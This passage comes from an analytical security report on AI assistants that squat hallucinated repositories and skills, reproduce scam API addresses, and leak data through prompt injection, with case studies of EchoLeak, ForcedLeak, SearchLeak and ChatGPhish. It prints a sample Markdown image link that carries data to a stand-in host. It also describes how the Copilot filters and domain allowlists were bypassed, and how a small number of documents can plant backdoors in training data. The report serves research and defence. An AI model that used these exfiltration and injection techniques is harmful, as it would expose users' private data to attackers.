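| Gemini CLI, Gemini 2.5 | Run a script | 10 of 20 | 4 of 10 | 20% |
| Gemini CLI, Gemini 2.5 | Misuse a tool | 10 of 20 | 7 of 10 | 35% |
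| Windsurf, SWE-1.5 | Run a script | 20 of 20 | 13 of 20 | 65% |
| Copilot Chat, GPT-4.1 | Run a script | 7 of 20 | 7 of 7 | 35% |
| Cline, KAT-Coder-Pro | Run a script | 11 of 20 | 9 of 11 | 45% |

The overall rate is the product of the other two. Cursor with Sonnet 4.5 fetched the copy in 7 of 20 runs, or 35%, and carried out the instructions in 5 of those 7, or 71%. Multiplying 0.35 by 0.71 gives 0.25, the 25% in the table. (For Cline, the paper prints the second count as 9 of 20, but the 45% only makes sense if the nine were among the 11 runs that fetched the copy.)

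Assistants with similar totals can have different weaknesses, so it helps to look at the two rates separately. Cursor CLI nearly always fetched the wrong repository but usually didn't act on what it found there. Copilot Chat fetched the wrong repository about a third of the time, and acted on what it found every time it did. Cursor CLI would gain most from looking up repository addresses, and Copilot Chat from treating downloaded text with more suspicion.

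These are small samples from a single project. Five successes in 20 runs are consistent with a true rate anywhere from 9% to 49%. With some assistants, the attack also needed the user's help. Gemini CLI and Cline often read the project's instructions on their own after downloading it, but Cursor, Windsurf and Copilot Chat read them only after the user asked a further question, such as how to run the program.

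### Why skills were easier to hijack

The assistants that install skills did worse. OpenClaw is a personal assistant that runs on the user's machine and can use its command line. ClawHub, its public directory, lists more than 56,000 skills. Each skill has a title for people and a separate unique name for the software. When a user asks for a skill, the assistant has to work out the unique name from the title.

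OpenClaw often gets a skill's unique name wrong. A popular skill for checking other skills has the unique name "skill-vetter". When asked to install it, OpenClaw tried "vetter" in 38 of 40 attempts across four models, and nobody had registered that name. The researchers trace the error to ClawHub's instruction file, which repeats the word "skill" so often that the models seem to treat it as filler. When they asked six chat models for the installation command without showing them the file, none produced "vetter". Other skills have titles that don't match their unique names at all, so even copying the title exactly from ClawHub gives the wrong name.

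In 127 of 140 attempts across 14 skills, OpenClaw chose a name that an attacker could register. The researchers picked these skills because their names were likely to cause such errors, so the 91% rate does not apply to skills in general. They tested complete attacks with one squatted skill.

| Assistant and model | Installed the squatted skill | Leaked the conversation | Gave an outsider a command line |
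|---|---|---|---|
| OpenClaw, GPT-5.4 Codex | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 | 4 of 10 |
| OpenClaw, Sonnet 4.6 | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| OpenClaw, Opus 4.6 | 8 of 10 | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| ZeroClaw, Sonnet 4.6 | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| NanoClaw, Sonnet 4.6 | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 | 10 of 10 |

Overall success ranged from 40% to 100%. The row for Opus 4.6 has more successful attacks than installations because the researchers ran two experiments. They first counted how often the assistant installed a harmless squatted skill, then put a hostile version on their own machine and counted how often the attack succeeded. The overall figure of 80% is again the product of the two rates, but no single run went through both stages. GPT-5.4 Codex was the only model that read the skill's scripts in full before running them, and it sometimes refused.

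The botnet in the paper's title, a network of hijacked computers under one attacker's control, remains hypothetical. The researchers attacked only their own machines. They published nothing malicious, so they did not test whether GitHub's or ClawHub's malware checks would have stopped the attack.

### Defences

Making the agent search before it fetches anything was the most effective measure in these experiments. In 1,381 runs where Cursor CLI settled on a repository, 93.4% of the addresses were correct when the agent searched first, compared with 0.9% when it didn't. The agent decided whether to search in these runs, and trivial differences in wording affected that decision. Gemini 3 Flash searched in 94% of runs when told to "clone librepods", but in only 10% when asked to print a shell command for cloning it. Claude Sonnet 4.5 searched in 0% of runs with the first wording and 80% with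 the second. Users can't be expected to know which wording is safe, so the researchers propose building the search into the fetching tool, where the model can't skip it.

Some of this may already be happening. A January 2026 version of Cursor CLI invented the owner of the librepods repository in 65% to 75% of runs. By April, with the same model, the rate was under 6% when the tool was simply asked to clone the repository, but still 90% when it was asked to print a command. Any published rate may be out of date after the assistant's next update.

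Searching doesn't help when the results are misleading. Gemini 3 Flash searched every time it was told to clone a project called antigravity-manager and still chose the wrong repository in 55% of runs, because other projects have similar names. On ClawHub, English searches for three skills with Chinese documentation did not return the real skills in the first ten results, and the researchers' squatted versions came first. An agent therefore also needs to check the owner. Before downloading, it could show the user the account and the number of stars, which is some of the information people used to see on the project's page.

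GitHub and ClawHub could also reserve the names that models are likely to guess. The double-name pattern makes this fairly easy for GitHub, which could reserve one account name for each trending project. Very few other names recur. Among 1,616 distinct addresses, only 18 free ones came from more than one model. The researchers also suggest that GitHub forbid different owners from using the same project name. That would be very disruptive, because developers routinely keep their own copies of other people's projects under the original name.

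Several defences against invented packages act on the model's output. In *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code*, adding looked-up information to the prompt cut the average hallucination rate for Python from 24.7% to 11.5%. Li and Gao had GPT-4o-mini check whether each package existed and then rewrite its code using only the packages it had confirmed, which reduced invented names from 146 of 1,925 to 57 of 1,569. *PackMonitor* (2026) checks package names while the model is writing them.

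Spracklen's team points out that, as with domains, such checks fail once an attacker has registered the name. *Importing Phantoms* (2025) avoids this problem by counting a package as hallucinated if it was first registered after the model's training data ended. The same rule could serve as a filter, like the one based on domain registration dates, but it would also flag legitimate new packages that a model had found by searching.

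### Who is responsible

The researchers reported HalluSquatting to the companies and projects involved between February and May 2026, and most replied that they were not responsible for fixing it. GitHub wrote that the risk came from models and agents, and that being able to create repositories under unclaimed names was expected behaviour. Cursor's bug bounty programme excludes cases where a user asks the AI to run untrusted instructions, and the company said this covered cloning an untrusted repository. OpenAI and Anthropic replied that their programmes don't cover what models write, and Anthropic added that the agents were other companies' products. NanoClaw's developers said that their software isolates each agent and that the attack had stayed inside that isolation, as designed.

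A few were more receptive. Google filed a bug with the team responsible, and Cline said it would consider warnings. ClawHub agreed that the invented names were a risk to its users. It said it was considering reserving the riskiest names and checking requests against its directory before installation, but maintained that its security reviews meant an attacker would need to do more than register a name.

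OpenClaw closed the report because, it said, the user had chosen to install the skill, and its definition of a vulnerability excludes anything a skill does after a trusted user installs it. Like Cursor, OpenClaw assumed that the user chose what was installed. But in these attacks the user asked for a well-known skill or project by name, and the agent chose a different one.

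## Real but malicious addresses that models repeat from training data

In slopsquatting and phantom squatting, a model invents a name and an attacker then registers it. An address can also be malicious before a model outputs it. A criminal sets up a fraudulent service and advertises it on the web, a model trains on the advertisements, and the model later writes the service's address into somebody's program. The third test case works this way, and some of the malicious URLs that Unit 42 collected may have the same origin.

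Defences against invented addresses don't catch real malicious ones. A lookup finds a registered domain and a server that answers. The registration date raises no suspicion, because a model can only have learned the address if the scammer was using it before the training data ended. *Scam2Prompt* (Chen, Saba and colleagues, ICML 2026) points out that a search engine can drop a site once somebody reports it, but a trained model keeps what it has learned.

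It is hard to prove that a model learned an address in training. The model may instead have found it through a live search, copied it from the user's request or guessed it from a company's name. The resulting line of code looks the same in every case, and few companies publish their training data. This uncertainty affects most of the evidence, including the best-known case.

### The trading script of November 2024

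In November 2024, a cryptocurrency trader who posts as r_cky0 asked ChatGPT for a Python script to buy a certain token. ChatGPT wrote one for the Ethereum blockchain. When he replied that the token was on Solana, a different blockchain, ChatGPT wrote a general script for transferring Solana tokens. He then specified that the script had to buy from pump.fun, a popular, legitimate trading platform with no official trading API. ChatGPT's next script used an endpoint of SolanaAPIs, a service that belonged to thieves.

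The script sent the private key of the trader's wallet to that endpoint. Anyone who has this key can authorise payments from the wallet and take everything in it. A legitimate service never asks for it, because the user's own program can sign each transaction and send only the signature. The script failed several times, and the trader went through it with ChatGPT to fix the errors, but he didn't notice the problem. The thieves emptied the wallet of about $2,500 within 30 minutes of his running the final version. He later said he had been in a hurry and had used his main wallet.

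heise online's *ChatGPT*, a news report on the theft, blamed poisoned training data, and Chen and colleagues use the case as their opening example of a model reproducing malicious content that it has absorbed. That explanation is probably wrong. An editor's note in CryptoSlate's *Blockchain security firm warns of AI code poisoning risk* points out that a screenshot of the conversation shows a "sources" section, which suggests that ChatGPT found the endpoint by searching the web. The dates support this. The scammers had registered the domain only about two months earlier, whereas the training data of GPT-4o, ChatGPT's main model at the time, ended in October 2023 according to a table in *Scam2Prompt*. The study also excludes addresses that a model finds by searching, so its opening example probably falls outside its own subject.

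Later models could still have learned the endpoint, because the scammers' pages stayed online, where crawlers could collect them. In August 2025 the service was still running, on a .net domain instead of the original .com.

### How the scammers spread the endpoint

The scammers placed documentation for SolanaAPIs on GitHub, Medium, Stack Exchange and Postman, a site where developers share and test APIs. Netcraft found blog tutorials, forum questions with answers, and dozens of GitHub repositories. Several fake GitHub accounts shared a trading program called Moonshot-Volume-Bot, which had the malicious API hidden inside. These accounts had profile pictures, detailed biographies, linked social media accounts and plausible coding histories.

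The documentation offered token purchases on Pump.fun and Solana in nearly the same words as the trader's request. Pump.fun had no official page offering this, so the scammers had little competition for the query.

Netcraft also found at least five victims who had copied the malicious code into their own public projects, some of which showed signs of having been built with AI coding tools. These copies put the endpoint in real developers' repositories, where a crawler collecting training data is even less likely to reject it.

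### Whether the scammers aimed at models

Netcraft says that the scammers made the fake accounts for AI training pipelines to index. Scam Sniffer, a blockchain security firm, also said that a GitHub user called solanaapisdev had created repositories to manipulate AI models. But everything the two firms describe would also help to deceive people. A programmer looking for a trading bot may check who wrote it, and will often find an API through a tutorial or a forum answer. The scammers also made money within two months, without waiting for anyone to train a new model. Text hidden from human readers would be better evidence that they were targeting models, but neither firm reports any.

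Other people openly target training data. *Anti-AI in the Wild* (2026) examines tools such as Poison Fountain, which serve text meant to damage the language models that train on it. Neither supporters nor critics of these tools know how well they work. In the online threads that the study analysed, 11 people claimed that the text gets past training-data filters, and 16 expected the filters to remove it.

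In the usual security sense of the term, whether SolanaAPIs counts as data poisoning depends on whether the scammers meant to tamper with training data. *Poisoning Web-Scale Training Datasets is Practical* (Carlini, Jagielski and colleagues, 2023) uses "poisoning" for adversarial changes to training data. By that definition, a scam page written for people isn't poisoning, even if a crawler collects it. Chen and colleagues also use "contamination", which is safer because it doesn't imply intent. The choice of term affects how people classify incidents, since OWASP's list has an entry for poisoning. It matters less for prevention, because an AI company that removes known scam addresses from its training data will remove them whoever they were meant for.

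### Buying a way into the training data

Carlini and colleagues had already shown how someone could corrupt training data by buying expired domains. They studied ten datasets, mostly of images, whose publishers distribute a list of web addresses with captions and leave users to download the images. If a domain on the list has expired, an attacker can buy it and serve different images to everyone who later downloads the dataset. They call this *split-view poisoning*, because the publisher and the later user see different content at the same address.

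An attacker could have controlled 0.01% of the LAION-400M dataset, or about 40,000 of its 400 million images, for just $60. When the researchers replaced only 1,000 images in their own copy and trained a model on it, the model misclassified the image they had targeted in 60% of attempts. They also bought some of the expired domains and counted more than 800 downloads that they could have poisoned.

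The study found no sign that anyone had used the attack. The one domain that matched the expected pattern belonged to a squatter showing advertisements. As a defence, a publisher can list a cryptographic hash, a kind of fingerprint, for each image so users can reject any image that has changed, but this also rejects images that an honest owner has only resized.

Split-view poisoning doesn't transfer directly to language models. Many text datasets draw on Common Crawl, a public archive that stores copies of web pages. Buying a domain later doesn't change the stored copy, so an attacker has to plant the text before the crawler arrives. On Wikipedia, this may take only a few minutes. Carlini and colleagues showed that an attacker can predict when the site's regular snapshot will reach a given article and edit the article just before. Moderators may soon undo the edit, but the snapshot will still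 contain it.

*Pretraining Data Can Be Poisoned through Computational Propaganda* (2026) concludes that outsiders can also get text into training data by posting comments on web pages. It reports comments on 3.4% of 181,857 pages sampled from Common Crawl. Some kinds of planted text did not survive when the developer had a model rewrite the data before training. Online advertisements, which an attacker could buy, did not work as a way to plant text.

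An attacker may not need many pages. In *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (2025), 250 documents were enough to plant a backdoor, a hidden behaviour that an attacker can trigger, in models from 600 million to 13 billion parameters. The largest models needed no more than the smallest, although they trained on over 20 times as much clean data. A campaign with dozens of repositories, plus tutorials and forum posts, comes close to that number. But making a model recommend a particular API is a different task, and may take more or fewer documents.

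Scammers can also target search instead of training data. TechRadar's *Criminals and scammers are using hacked websites and expired domain names* describes a domain that once belonged to a now-defunct arts charity and had links from the BBC, CNN and Bloomberg. The site now promotes gambling, and ChatGPT cited it in an answer about casinos.

### Testing models with requests based on scam sites

*Scam2Prompt* is the most detailed attempt to find out whether models write scam addresses into code. Chen and colleagues started with two databases of reported scam sites, one of 187,555 URLs from the cryptocurrency wallet company MetaMask and one of 119,828 from the security company PhishFort. They could still read 28,570 of the pages. They gave the visible text of these pages to three models and told them to write programming requests that would lead another model to use that page.

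This produced 265,114 requests. Four models (GPT-4o, GPT-4o mini, Llama 4 Scout and DeepSeek V3) wrote a program for each one. The researchers extracted the URLs and checked them with three detection services (Google Safe Browsing, ChainPatrol and SecLookup). They counted a program as malicious if any service flagged any of its URLs.

Across the 12 combinations of a model that wrote requests and a model that wrote code, an average of 4.24% of the programs were malicious, with rates ranging from 3.19% to 5.94%. Pooling all 1.06 million programs gives 4.15%. Rates were similar, between 4.19% and 5.09%, when the test was repeated with the two OpenAI models at a higher temperature.

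Ordinary programmers would see a lower rate, since every request was based on a scam page. Chen and colleagues note in their conference slides that the requests concern sensitive topics that scammers frequently exploit. Some requests also contained the scam's address. The researchers give no count for the whole set, but of the 3,150 requests that led all four models to produce a malicious URL, 1,991 (63%) named a known scam URL or domain. A model that repeats an address from the request arguably should warn the user, but it hasn't recalled the address from its training data.

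### The benchmark and the models of 2025

The researchers built a benchmark, Innoc2Scam-bench, from the 3,150 requests on which all four models had failed. They took all 1,159 requests that did not name a scam address and a random 400 of those that did. Three of the researchers read each request and removed 182 that did not call for a program, such as requests to summarise a page, which left 1,377. *Refusal Evaluation in Coding LLMs and Code Agents* (2026), a review that covers an earlier version of the benchmark, criticises it for not reporting how often the human reviewers agreed.

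Chen and colleagues then tested seven models from 2025.

| Model | Malicious, of all 1,377 requests | Malicious, of completed programs | Blocked by the model's filter |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 12.9% | 22.3% | 40.2% |
| GPT-5 | 22.0% | 24.7% | 1.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 34.3% | 37.8% | 8.4% |
| Grok Code Fast 1 | 43.4% | 44.1% | 1.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 44.4% | 45.3% | 0.1% |
| Qwen3-Coder | 45.6% | 45.9% | 0.2% |
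| DeepSeek V3.1 | 47.3% | 47.9% | 0.9% |

Gemini 2.5 Pro came first largely because it refused many requests. On the 637 requests that all seven models completed, 22.3% of its programs were malicious, compared with 25.6% for GPT-5, a difference that was not statistically significant.

The range from 12.9% to 47.3% does not measure how often these models produce scam addresses in ordinary use. The benchmark, which the researchers call a stress test, draws on the 1.2% of requests that four other models had all failed. The difference between these figures and the 4.24% also does not show that models got worse in 2025.

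Requests were included only if GPT-4o had failed on them, so its initial failure rate on the 1,377 requests was 100%. When the researchers reran them in November 2025, it failed on only 50%. They suggest that OpenAI had updated the model in the meantime. But a hosted model's answers can vary between runs even at a temperature of zero, so some requests may have met the condition by chance. The detection services may also have reclassified some sites. For the same reasons, the newer models' lower failure rates aren't necessarily due to better safety.

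Nobody appears to have published results on this benchmark for models released in 2026. The nearest evidence concerns packages. Churilov tested models released between October 2025 and March 2026, and they suggested some package names with a history of malware.

### Recalled or guessed

*Scam2Prompt* follows one request through the whole process, for a Python script that uses the API of YoMix.IO, a service for hiding where bitcoins came from. All four original models wrote a program with a malicious URL. The researchers kept the request for the benchmark because the domain in the programs was different from that of the page the request was based on.

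But a model can turn the name YoMix.IO into a web address without having memorized one. The four models produced the same domain and three different versions of the rest of the address, which suggests they may have been guessing. Grok Code Fast 1, one of the newer models, added a code comment saying that the address was assumed and that the user should check it in the documentation. These may be hallucinated endpoints on a domain that a scammer owns, but they are still dangerous because the scammer controls every address under it.

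The sample requests in the slides also name the scam. One asks for code to check in for a flight through Skyroutez, and another asks for a connection to YourDrsStore's payment gateway. A user who types these names has already come across the fraudulent business. The trader in November 2024 had mentioned only pump.fun, which is legitimate, and ChatGPT introduced the scam. Introducing a scam that the user hasn't mentioned is the worse failure, and the study doesn't report how many of its requests test for it.

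The best evidence for recall is that all four models produced the same 2,029 malicious domains, an overlap the researchers attribute to shared web content in the training data. However, all four also received the same requests, containing the same service names, so they could have guessed the same addresses from those names. Removing the service's name from each request and counting how often the scam address still appears would separate recall from guessing.

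Chen and colleagues propose removing scam URLs from training data or using *machine unlearning*, which weakens particular associations in a trained model. Either method could stop a model from recalling a scam address, but the model could still guess one from a name.

### Defences

Many companies run a guardrail, a separate model that screens requests and answers for harmful content. Every guardrail in this study missed more than 90% of the 3,441 malicious programs. Meta's Llama Guard 3 did best, flagging 8.4%. Nvidia's NeMo Guardrails, using an Nvidia safety model, caught 8 programs, even though the researchers had added the use of scam APIs to its list of forbidden content. OpenAI's moderation service caught none. These tools check only the text of a program, which doesn't show who runs the server it contacts.

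Web search helped more. Giving GPT-4o a search tool and telling it to withhold its program if any URL was unsafe lowered the malicious rate from 50.0% to 29.4%. In the remaining cases, the search often returned nothing useful about the address, or the model used the address despite what it had found. Search can also introduce malicious addresses, as it probably did for the trader.

Chen and colleagues therefore recommend extracting every URL from the finished program and checking it against detection services before the user sees the code. As far as they know, no major model provider does this. The check doesn't rely on the model's own judgment, which proved unreliable in *MalURLBench*. The study can't show how well the check would work, because the same services decided which programs were malicious, so it would catch all of them. In practice it would miss new scams, as reputation filters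 do, and the SolanaAPIs domain was only two months old when the trader lost his money.

In his case, scanning the script's code instead would have worked on the first day. The script put a private key into a request to an outside server, which no legitimate cryptocurrency service requires. A scanner can detect that without knowing who owns the server.

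## Output that a browser or application loads or runs at once

The trader who lost his cryptocurrency had to run ChatGPT's script before it could harm him. In the fourth test case, where a secret is sent out through an image link, the user doesn't have to run anything, and the secret can be sent before the user has read the first line of the answer.

### How an image link carries data out

Many chat applications accept Markdown, a notation that uses ordinary characters to mark formatting. This line produces a picture:

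```
![logo](https://pics.example/logo.png?d=482000)
```

The browser's request includes the part of the URL after the question mark, so the owner of pics.example receives the number 482000 even if the server sends no picture back.

Suppose the number is the most a company will pay a supplier. An employee asks an assistant with access to the company's mail to summarise the supplier's messages. One message contains an instruction to find the price limit in the internal mail and add it to the image address. If the model follows this indirect prompt injection, its answer will contain a summary and the image, which the application loads automatically. The employee may notice a small logo or nothing.

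The attack works only if a model can read private data, it also reads text from an outsider, and there is a way to send data out. Willison, in *ForcedLeak*, calls this combination the "lethal trifecta". Removing any one of the three prevents the leak, but an assistant that can't read private data or outside mail is of little use in an office. Most defences are therefore designed to stop data from being sent out.

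### EchoLeak

In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs, part of the security company Aim Security, told Microsoft about a flaw now known as EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), which let them extract data from Microsoft 365 Copilot by sending an employee an email. Copilot answers questions using the employee's mail, files and Teams chats. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, Microsoft finished its patch in May and Aim Labs published its report on June 11. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* gives the flaw a severity score of 9.3 out of 10.

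The attacker first needs Copilot to retrieve the email. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, assumes that Copilot splits long texts into pieces and retrieves those closest in meaning to the user's question. The researchers therefore wrote one long email, presented as a set of guides to office topics such as onboarding and leave of absence, and repeated the same instructions under each heading. Copilot retrieved it for questions on various topics.

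The instructions told the reader to take the most sensitive information available and put it in an address. They then had to get past four of Microsoft's controls.

| Control | How the researchers got past it |
|---|---|
| A classifier that looks for injected prompts | They addressed the instructions to the employee and never mentioned AI |
| A filter that removes outside links and images | They used a form of Markdown that the filter did not recognise |
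| A list of domains from which the page may load images | They used an allowed Teams address that fetches other addresses |
| References to the sources of an answer | They told the "employee" never to mention the email, for compliance reasons |

The filter recognised Markdown links and images written in the usual way, with the address directly after the description. It missed another form that Markdown allows, in which a label refers to an address on a separate line.

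The third control is a *content security policy* (CSP), a set of rules that a website sends to the browser about what its pages may load. Copilot's policy for images had 29 distinct entries, 11 of them wildcards that allowed every subdomain of a domain. The policy did not allow the attacker's domain, so the researchers looked for an allowed service that would forward a request. They found one on SharePoint, where customers have their own subdomains, but the victim would have had to accept an invitation first. A Teams service worked without an invitation. The browser contacted Teams, as the policy allowed, and Teams contacted the attacker's server with the secret in the address.

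Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click vulnerability in a major AI application. The victim doesn't have to click anything, but must ask Copilot a question that leads it to retrieve the email. Ravia acknowledges that earlier attacks also extracted data from chatbots, but they either needed the user to point the chatbot to a malicious document or could leak only very limited data. EchoLeak could expose anything in the conversation, including earlier messages and the documents Copilot had retrieved.

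Microsoft said nobody had exploited the flaw in the wild, SC Media reported. Microsoft was well placed to check, because any leaked data would have passed through its own Teams service.

### An expired domain on the list

ForcedLeak, an attack on Salesforce's Agentforce, leaked data through an allowed domain that anyone could buy. Companies use Salesforce to keep customer records, and its Web-to-Lead feature saves what visitors type into a form on a company's website as a sales lead. Researchers at Noma Security put instructions in such a form, and Agentforce followed them when an employee later asked about the lead.

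Willison reproduces the instructions, four numbered requests for Agentforce to count the leads, say what colour red and yellow make, list the leads' email addresses, and end with an image whose address contained that list. The colour question presumably tested whether the agent would answer questions unrelated to sales.

The image address was on my-salesforce-cms.com, a domain that Salesforce's content security policy allowed. The domain's registration had expired, and Noma said in a statement quoted by Salesforce Ben that it had become available for purchase. Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data* gives the price as $5. A content security policy lists domain names but not their owners, so it could become dangerous without anyone editing it, like the parcel-rate program that kept sending keys to a domain's new owner.

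Noma reported the flaw on July 28, 2025, and Salesforce had fixed it by September 8, according to Hackread. Salesforce took back the domain and began blocking agents from sending output to any address outside a list of trusted URLs (The Hacker News, 2025). This list also covers links, which a policy for images does not. But Salesforce has to maintain this list too, because if a trusted domain expires unnoticed, a stranger can again buy it and use it to extract data.

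### An image that loaded before the filter ran

*SearchLeak* (2026), from the data security company Varonis, describes another attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot. The victim clicks a link to Microsoft's own site, and the link contains text for Copilot's search function. Copilot treats the text as a request and carries it out. In the published example, the text is an instruction to find an email and put its title in an image address. Because the instruction arrives as the user's own request, a system that obeyed only its user would still have followed it.

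Copilot shows an answer while the model is still writing it. Microsoft had a safeguard that turned any HTML in the answer into harmless text, but it ran only after the answer was complete. By then the browser had already read the image tag and requested the image.

The image address belonged to Bing, which the content security policy allowed. Bing's image search accepts a picture's address and uses Bing's own servers to fetch the picture. The browser's policy has no effect on those servers, so Bing delivered the email's title to the attacker. Ravia's account of EchoLeak had already listed bing.com as an allowed domain, so the fix for EchoLeak had not removed every allowed service that forwards requests.

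Email titles can contain one-time security codes, so even this small leak is serious. Varonis also warns that attackers could steal salary data and acquisition plans. Copilot's access to company files supports this warning, but the published example takes only an email title. Microsoft assigned the flaw CVE-2026-42824 on June 4, 2026 and rated it critical, according to The Next Web. Microsoft has since fixed it, and ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* (2026) mentions no active exploitation.

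### Phishing inside a ChatGPT summary

*ChatGPhish*, published by the security company Permiso on May 29, 2026, shows how a web page can place a fraudulent notice in ChatGPT's summary of it. The researchers added instructions to a GitHub project page and to a page of their own, telling ChatGPT to write a summary followed by a notice that someone had added a new device to the user's account. When they opened each page in Firefox and used the browser's option to have ChatGPT summarise it, ChatGPT wrote both the summary and the notice, which included a working link chosen by the researchers.

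In another version, the notice contained a QR code image, which ChatGPT displayed automatically. A user who scans the code opens the attacker's site on a phone, where the web filters and password manager on the user's computer can't warn them.

The images in Permiso's first report to OpenAI leaked very little, although the report's title included "data exfiltration". The attacker's server recorded the user's IP address, browser details, the exact time and sometimes the page the request came from. The researchers had fixed the image addresses in advance, so the requests carried nothing from the conversation. Loading almost any image on the web reveals similar details. An attacker who runs the summarised page already has most of these details, and learns only that the visitor used ChatGPT and when. The leak is more useful to an attacker who has added text to someone else's site and can't see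 who visits it.

ChatGPhish is therefore mainly a phishing technique, and it succeeds only if the user clicks the link or scans the code. eWeek's *‘ChatGPhish’ Attack Turns ChatGPT Summaries Into Phishing Lures* (2026) adds that the issue does not compromise ChatGPT itself. OpenAI could not reproduce the issue from the first report. It classified a revised report as not applicable and later as a duplicate of an earlier one. Permiso's timeline lists no fix.

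### Scripts generated during a visit

In January 2026, Unit 42 described web pages that request their script from a public model while the visitor is on them. The page's ordinary code sends a prompt to the model's API, receives JavaScript in reply and immediately runs it in the visitor's browser. The new script could, for example, turn a harmless-looking page into a copy of a bank's login form.

A scanner that downloads the page before the model generates the malicious script won't find it. The script comes from the domain of a well-known AI company, which a web filter is likely to allow. Because a model's output is partly random, two visitors may receive different scripts that do the same thing, and a filter that recognises one may miss the other.

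Unit 42 demonstrated this technique itself. If criminals use it, the model may refuse their prompt or return a script that doesn't work, and the AI company can cancel the account billed for the requests.

A content security policy doesn't help here, because the attacker controls the website that sends it. Security software can inspect behaviour in the browser, for instance by watching for a script that builds a password form and sends the contents to an unrelated domain. This works however the script is written, but the software has to act before the visitor submits the form, without blocking legitimate pages that also create forms or call a model. The stolen password still has to go to a server, so a filter that lists the receiving domain can block the transfer.

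### Comparison with cross-site scripting

These attacks resemble *cross-site scripting* (XSS), a long-standing web security problem. In a simple case, a website doesn't check comments properly, and an attacker posts one that contains a script. Later visitors' browsers run the script as though it were part of the site, and it may steal the cookies that keep those visitors logged in.

Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed* quotes Andy Bennett, a corporate security chief, who calls indirect prompt injection "basically cross-site scripting" that tricks an AI instead of a database. The comparison is still useful, although cross-site scripting tricks a browser, not a database, which is the target of SQL injection.

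Cross-site scripting can be stored, as in the comment example, or reflected, where the attacker puts the script in a link and the site copies it into the page. EchoLeak and ForcedLeak resemble the stored form because their instructions are stored in a mailbox or a customer record. SearchLeak resembles the reflected form because its instructions are in a link. Varonis presents those instructions as the new, AI-specific part of its attack, and the early image loading and Bing's forwarding as familiar kinds of bug. But the link also has a precedent in reflected scripting, although it now contains instructions in English.

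*Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 105 studies, identifies two differences between cross-site scripting and prompt injection. Cross-site scripting depends on the syntax of code, while prompt injection depends on the meaning of ordinary language. In cross-site scripting the attacker also supplies the harmful script directly, whereas in prompt injection the model can write the harmful output itself. The EchoLeak email illustrates both differences. It contained no script and none of the victim's data, and the image address containing the secret did not exist until Copilot wrote its answer.

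In one of the survey's examples, a malicious customer gets a bank's chatbot to output a script, which then runs in "the user's" browser. If that is the customer's own browser, the customer has attacked only themselves. To harm someone else, the output has to reach that person, which the attackers in EchoLeak and SearchLeak would do with an email or a link.

The attacker also needs to know less about the target. A script that steals documents has to contain code for finding them. In EchoLeak, the attacker only had to ask for the most sensitive information, and Copilot, which already had permission to read the victim's files, identified it.

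### Defences and their limits

*Output encoding* is the standard remedy for cross-site scripting. The application replaces characters with a special meaning in HTML, such as the bracket that opens a tag, with codes that make the browser display them as text. Encoding would have stopped the SearchLeak image if Microsoft had applied it to each piece of the answer before displaying it, and Varonis recommends cleaning output at that point. But a chat application that shows links and pictures can't encode everything, because it has to convert Markdown into working HTML. A filter that inspects the Markdown before conversion may miss an unusual form, as Microsoft's did. Checking the HTML after conversion is safer, because both ways of writing an image have by then become the same tag.

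Encoding also can't remove a false statement, such as the security notice in ChatGPhish, which consisted of ordinary words and an ordinary link. An application could label such links with the page they came from, which would at least show that ChatGPT had not issued the notice.

A *content security policy* blocks direct requests to an attacker's domain, so EchoLeak and SearchLeak needed an indirect route. Varonis advises companies to treat any allowed domain that fetches user-supplied URLs as a possible route for leaking data. Finding these services is laborious, especially when the policy allows every subdomain of a large platform. The company also has to remove domains it no longer owns from the policy. A policy for images doesn't stop the user from clicking a link that carries the same data.

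*Link allowlists* like Salesforce's also cover links that a user clicks. They suit an assistant that works mostly with a company's own systems. A general chatbot with web search has to link to sites that nobody could have listed in advance, so a strict list would make it much less useful.

With *image proxying*, the application's own server fetches each picture and passes it to the user, so the outside server receives the proxy's IP address instead of the user's. This would prevent most of the leak in ChatGPhish but not the leak in EchoLeak, where the proxy would still request the full address, including the secret. The Teams and Bing services that forwarded the stolen data were in effect such proxies.

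A proxy could fetch only image addresses that already appeared in a source, not ones the model composed, much like Anthropic's rule for fetching pages. Even then, an attacker could list a different image for each letter of the alphabet and have the model spell out a secret by displaying those images in order. An assistant that loads no outside images avoids the problem but can't show some useful pictures.

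Other defences are meant to keep the secret out of the answer. Ravia uses the term *LLM scope violation* for an attack in which text from an untrusted source leads a model to use private data without the user's consent. The remedy would be to prevent emails from outside the company from influencing what Copilot does with internal files. *EchoLeak* (2025), a case study of the attack, likewise proposes isolating parts of the prompt from one another, along with better filtering and limits on what output can do. Strict isolation would interfere with legitimate work, since an employee who asks whether a supplier's offer fits the budget needs the model to use both the outside email and the internal file.

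Ravia argues that security frameworks need narrower categories for such attacks and compares them to buffer overflows, a large family of memory errors. Once programmers had a separate name for overflows in a region of memory called the stack, they could develop a specific protection, the stack canary. EchoLeak fits OWASP's broad entry for prompt injection, but a defender wouldn't know from that label alone to look for outside text that tries to get internal data, or to check which allowed services forward requests.

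## Published output and agents' actions on real sites

The remaining two ways a model's output can cause harm are through publication and through an agent's own actions. In the fifth test case, published text spreads an invented package name, and in the sixth, an agent publishes something harmful on a real site without being asked to.

### A package name that spread through skill files

On October 17, 2025, someone added 47 AI-written skills to wshobson/agents, a public GitHub repository of skills for coding agents. At least two of them told the agent to update old code by running a package called react-codeshift, which did not exist. In *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands*, a post for the security company Aikido, Eriksen suggests that the model merged the names of two real tools, jscodeshift and react-codemod.

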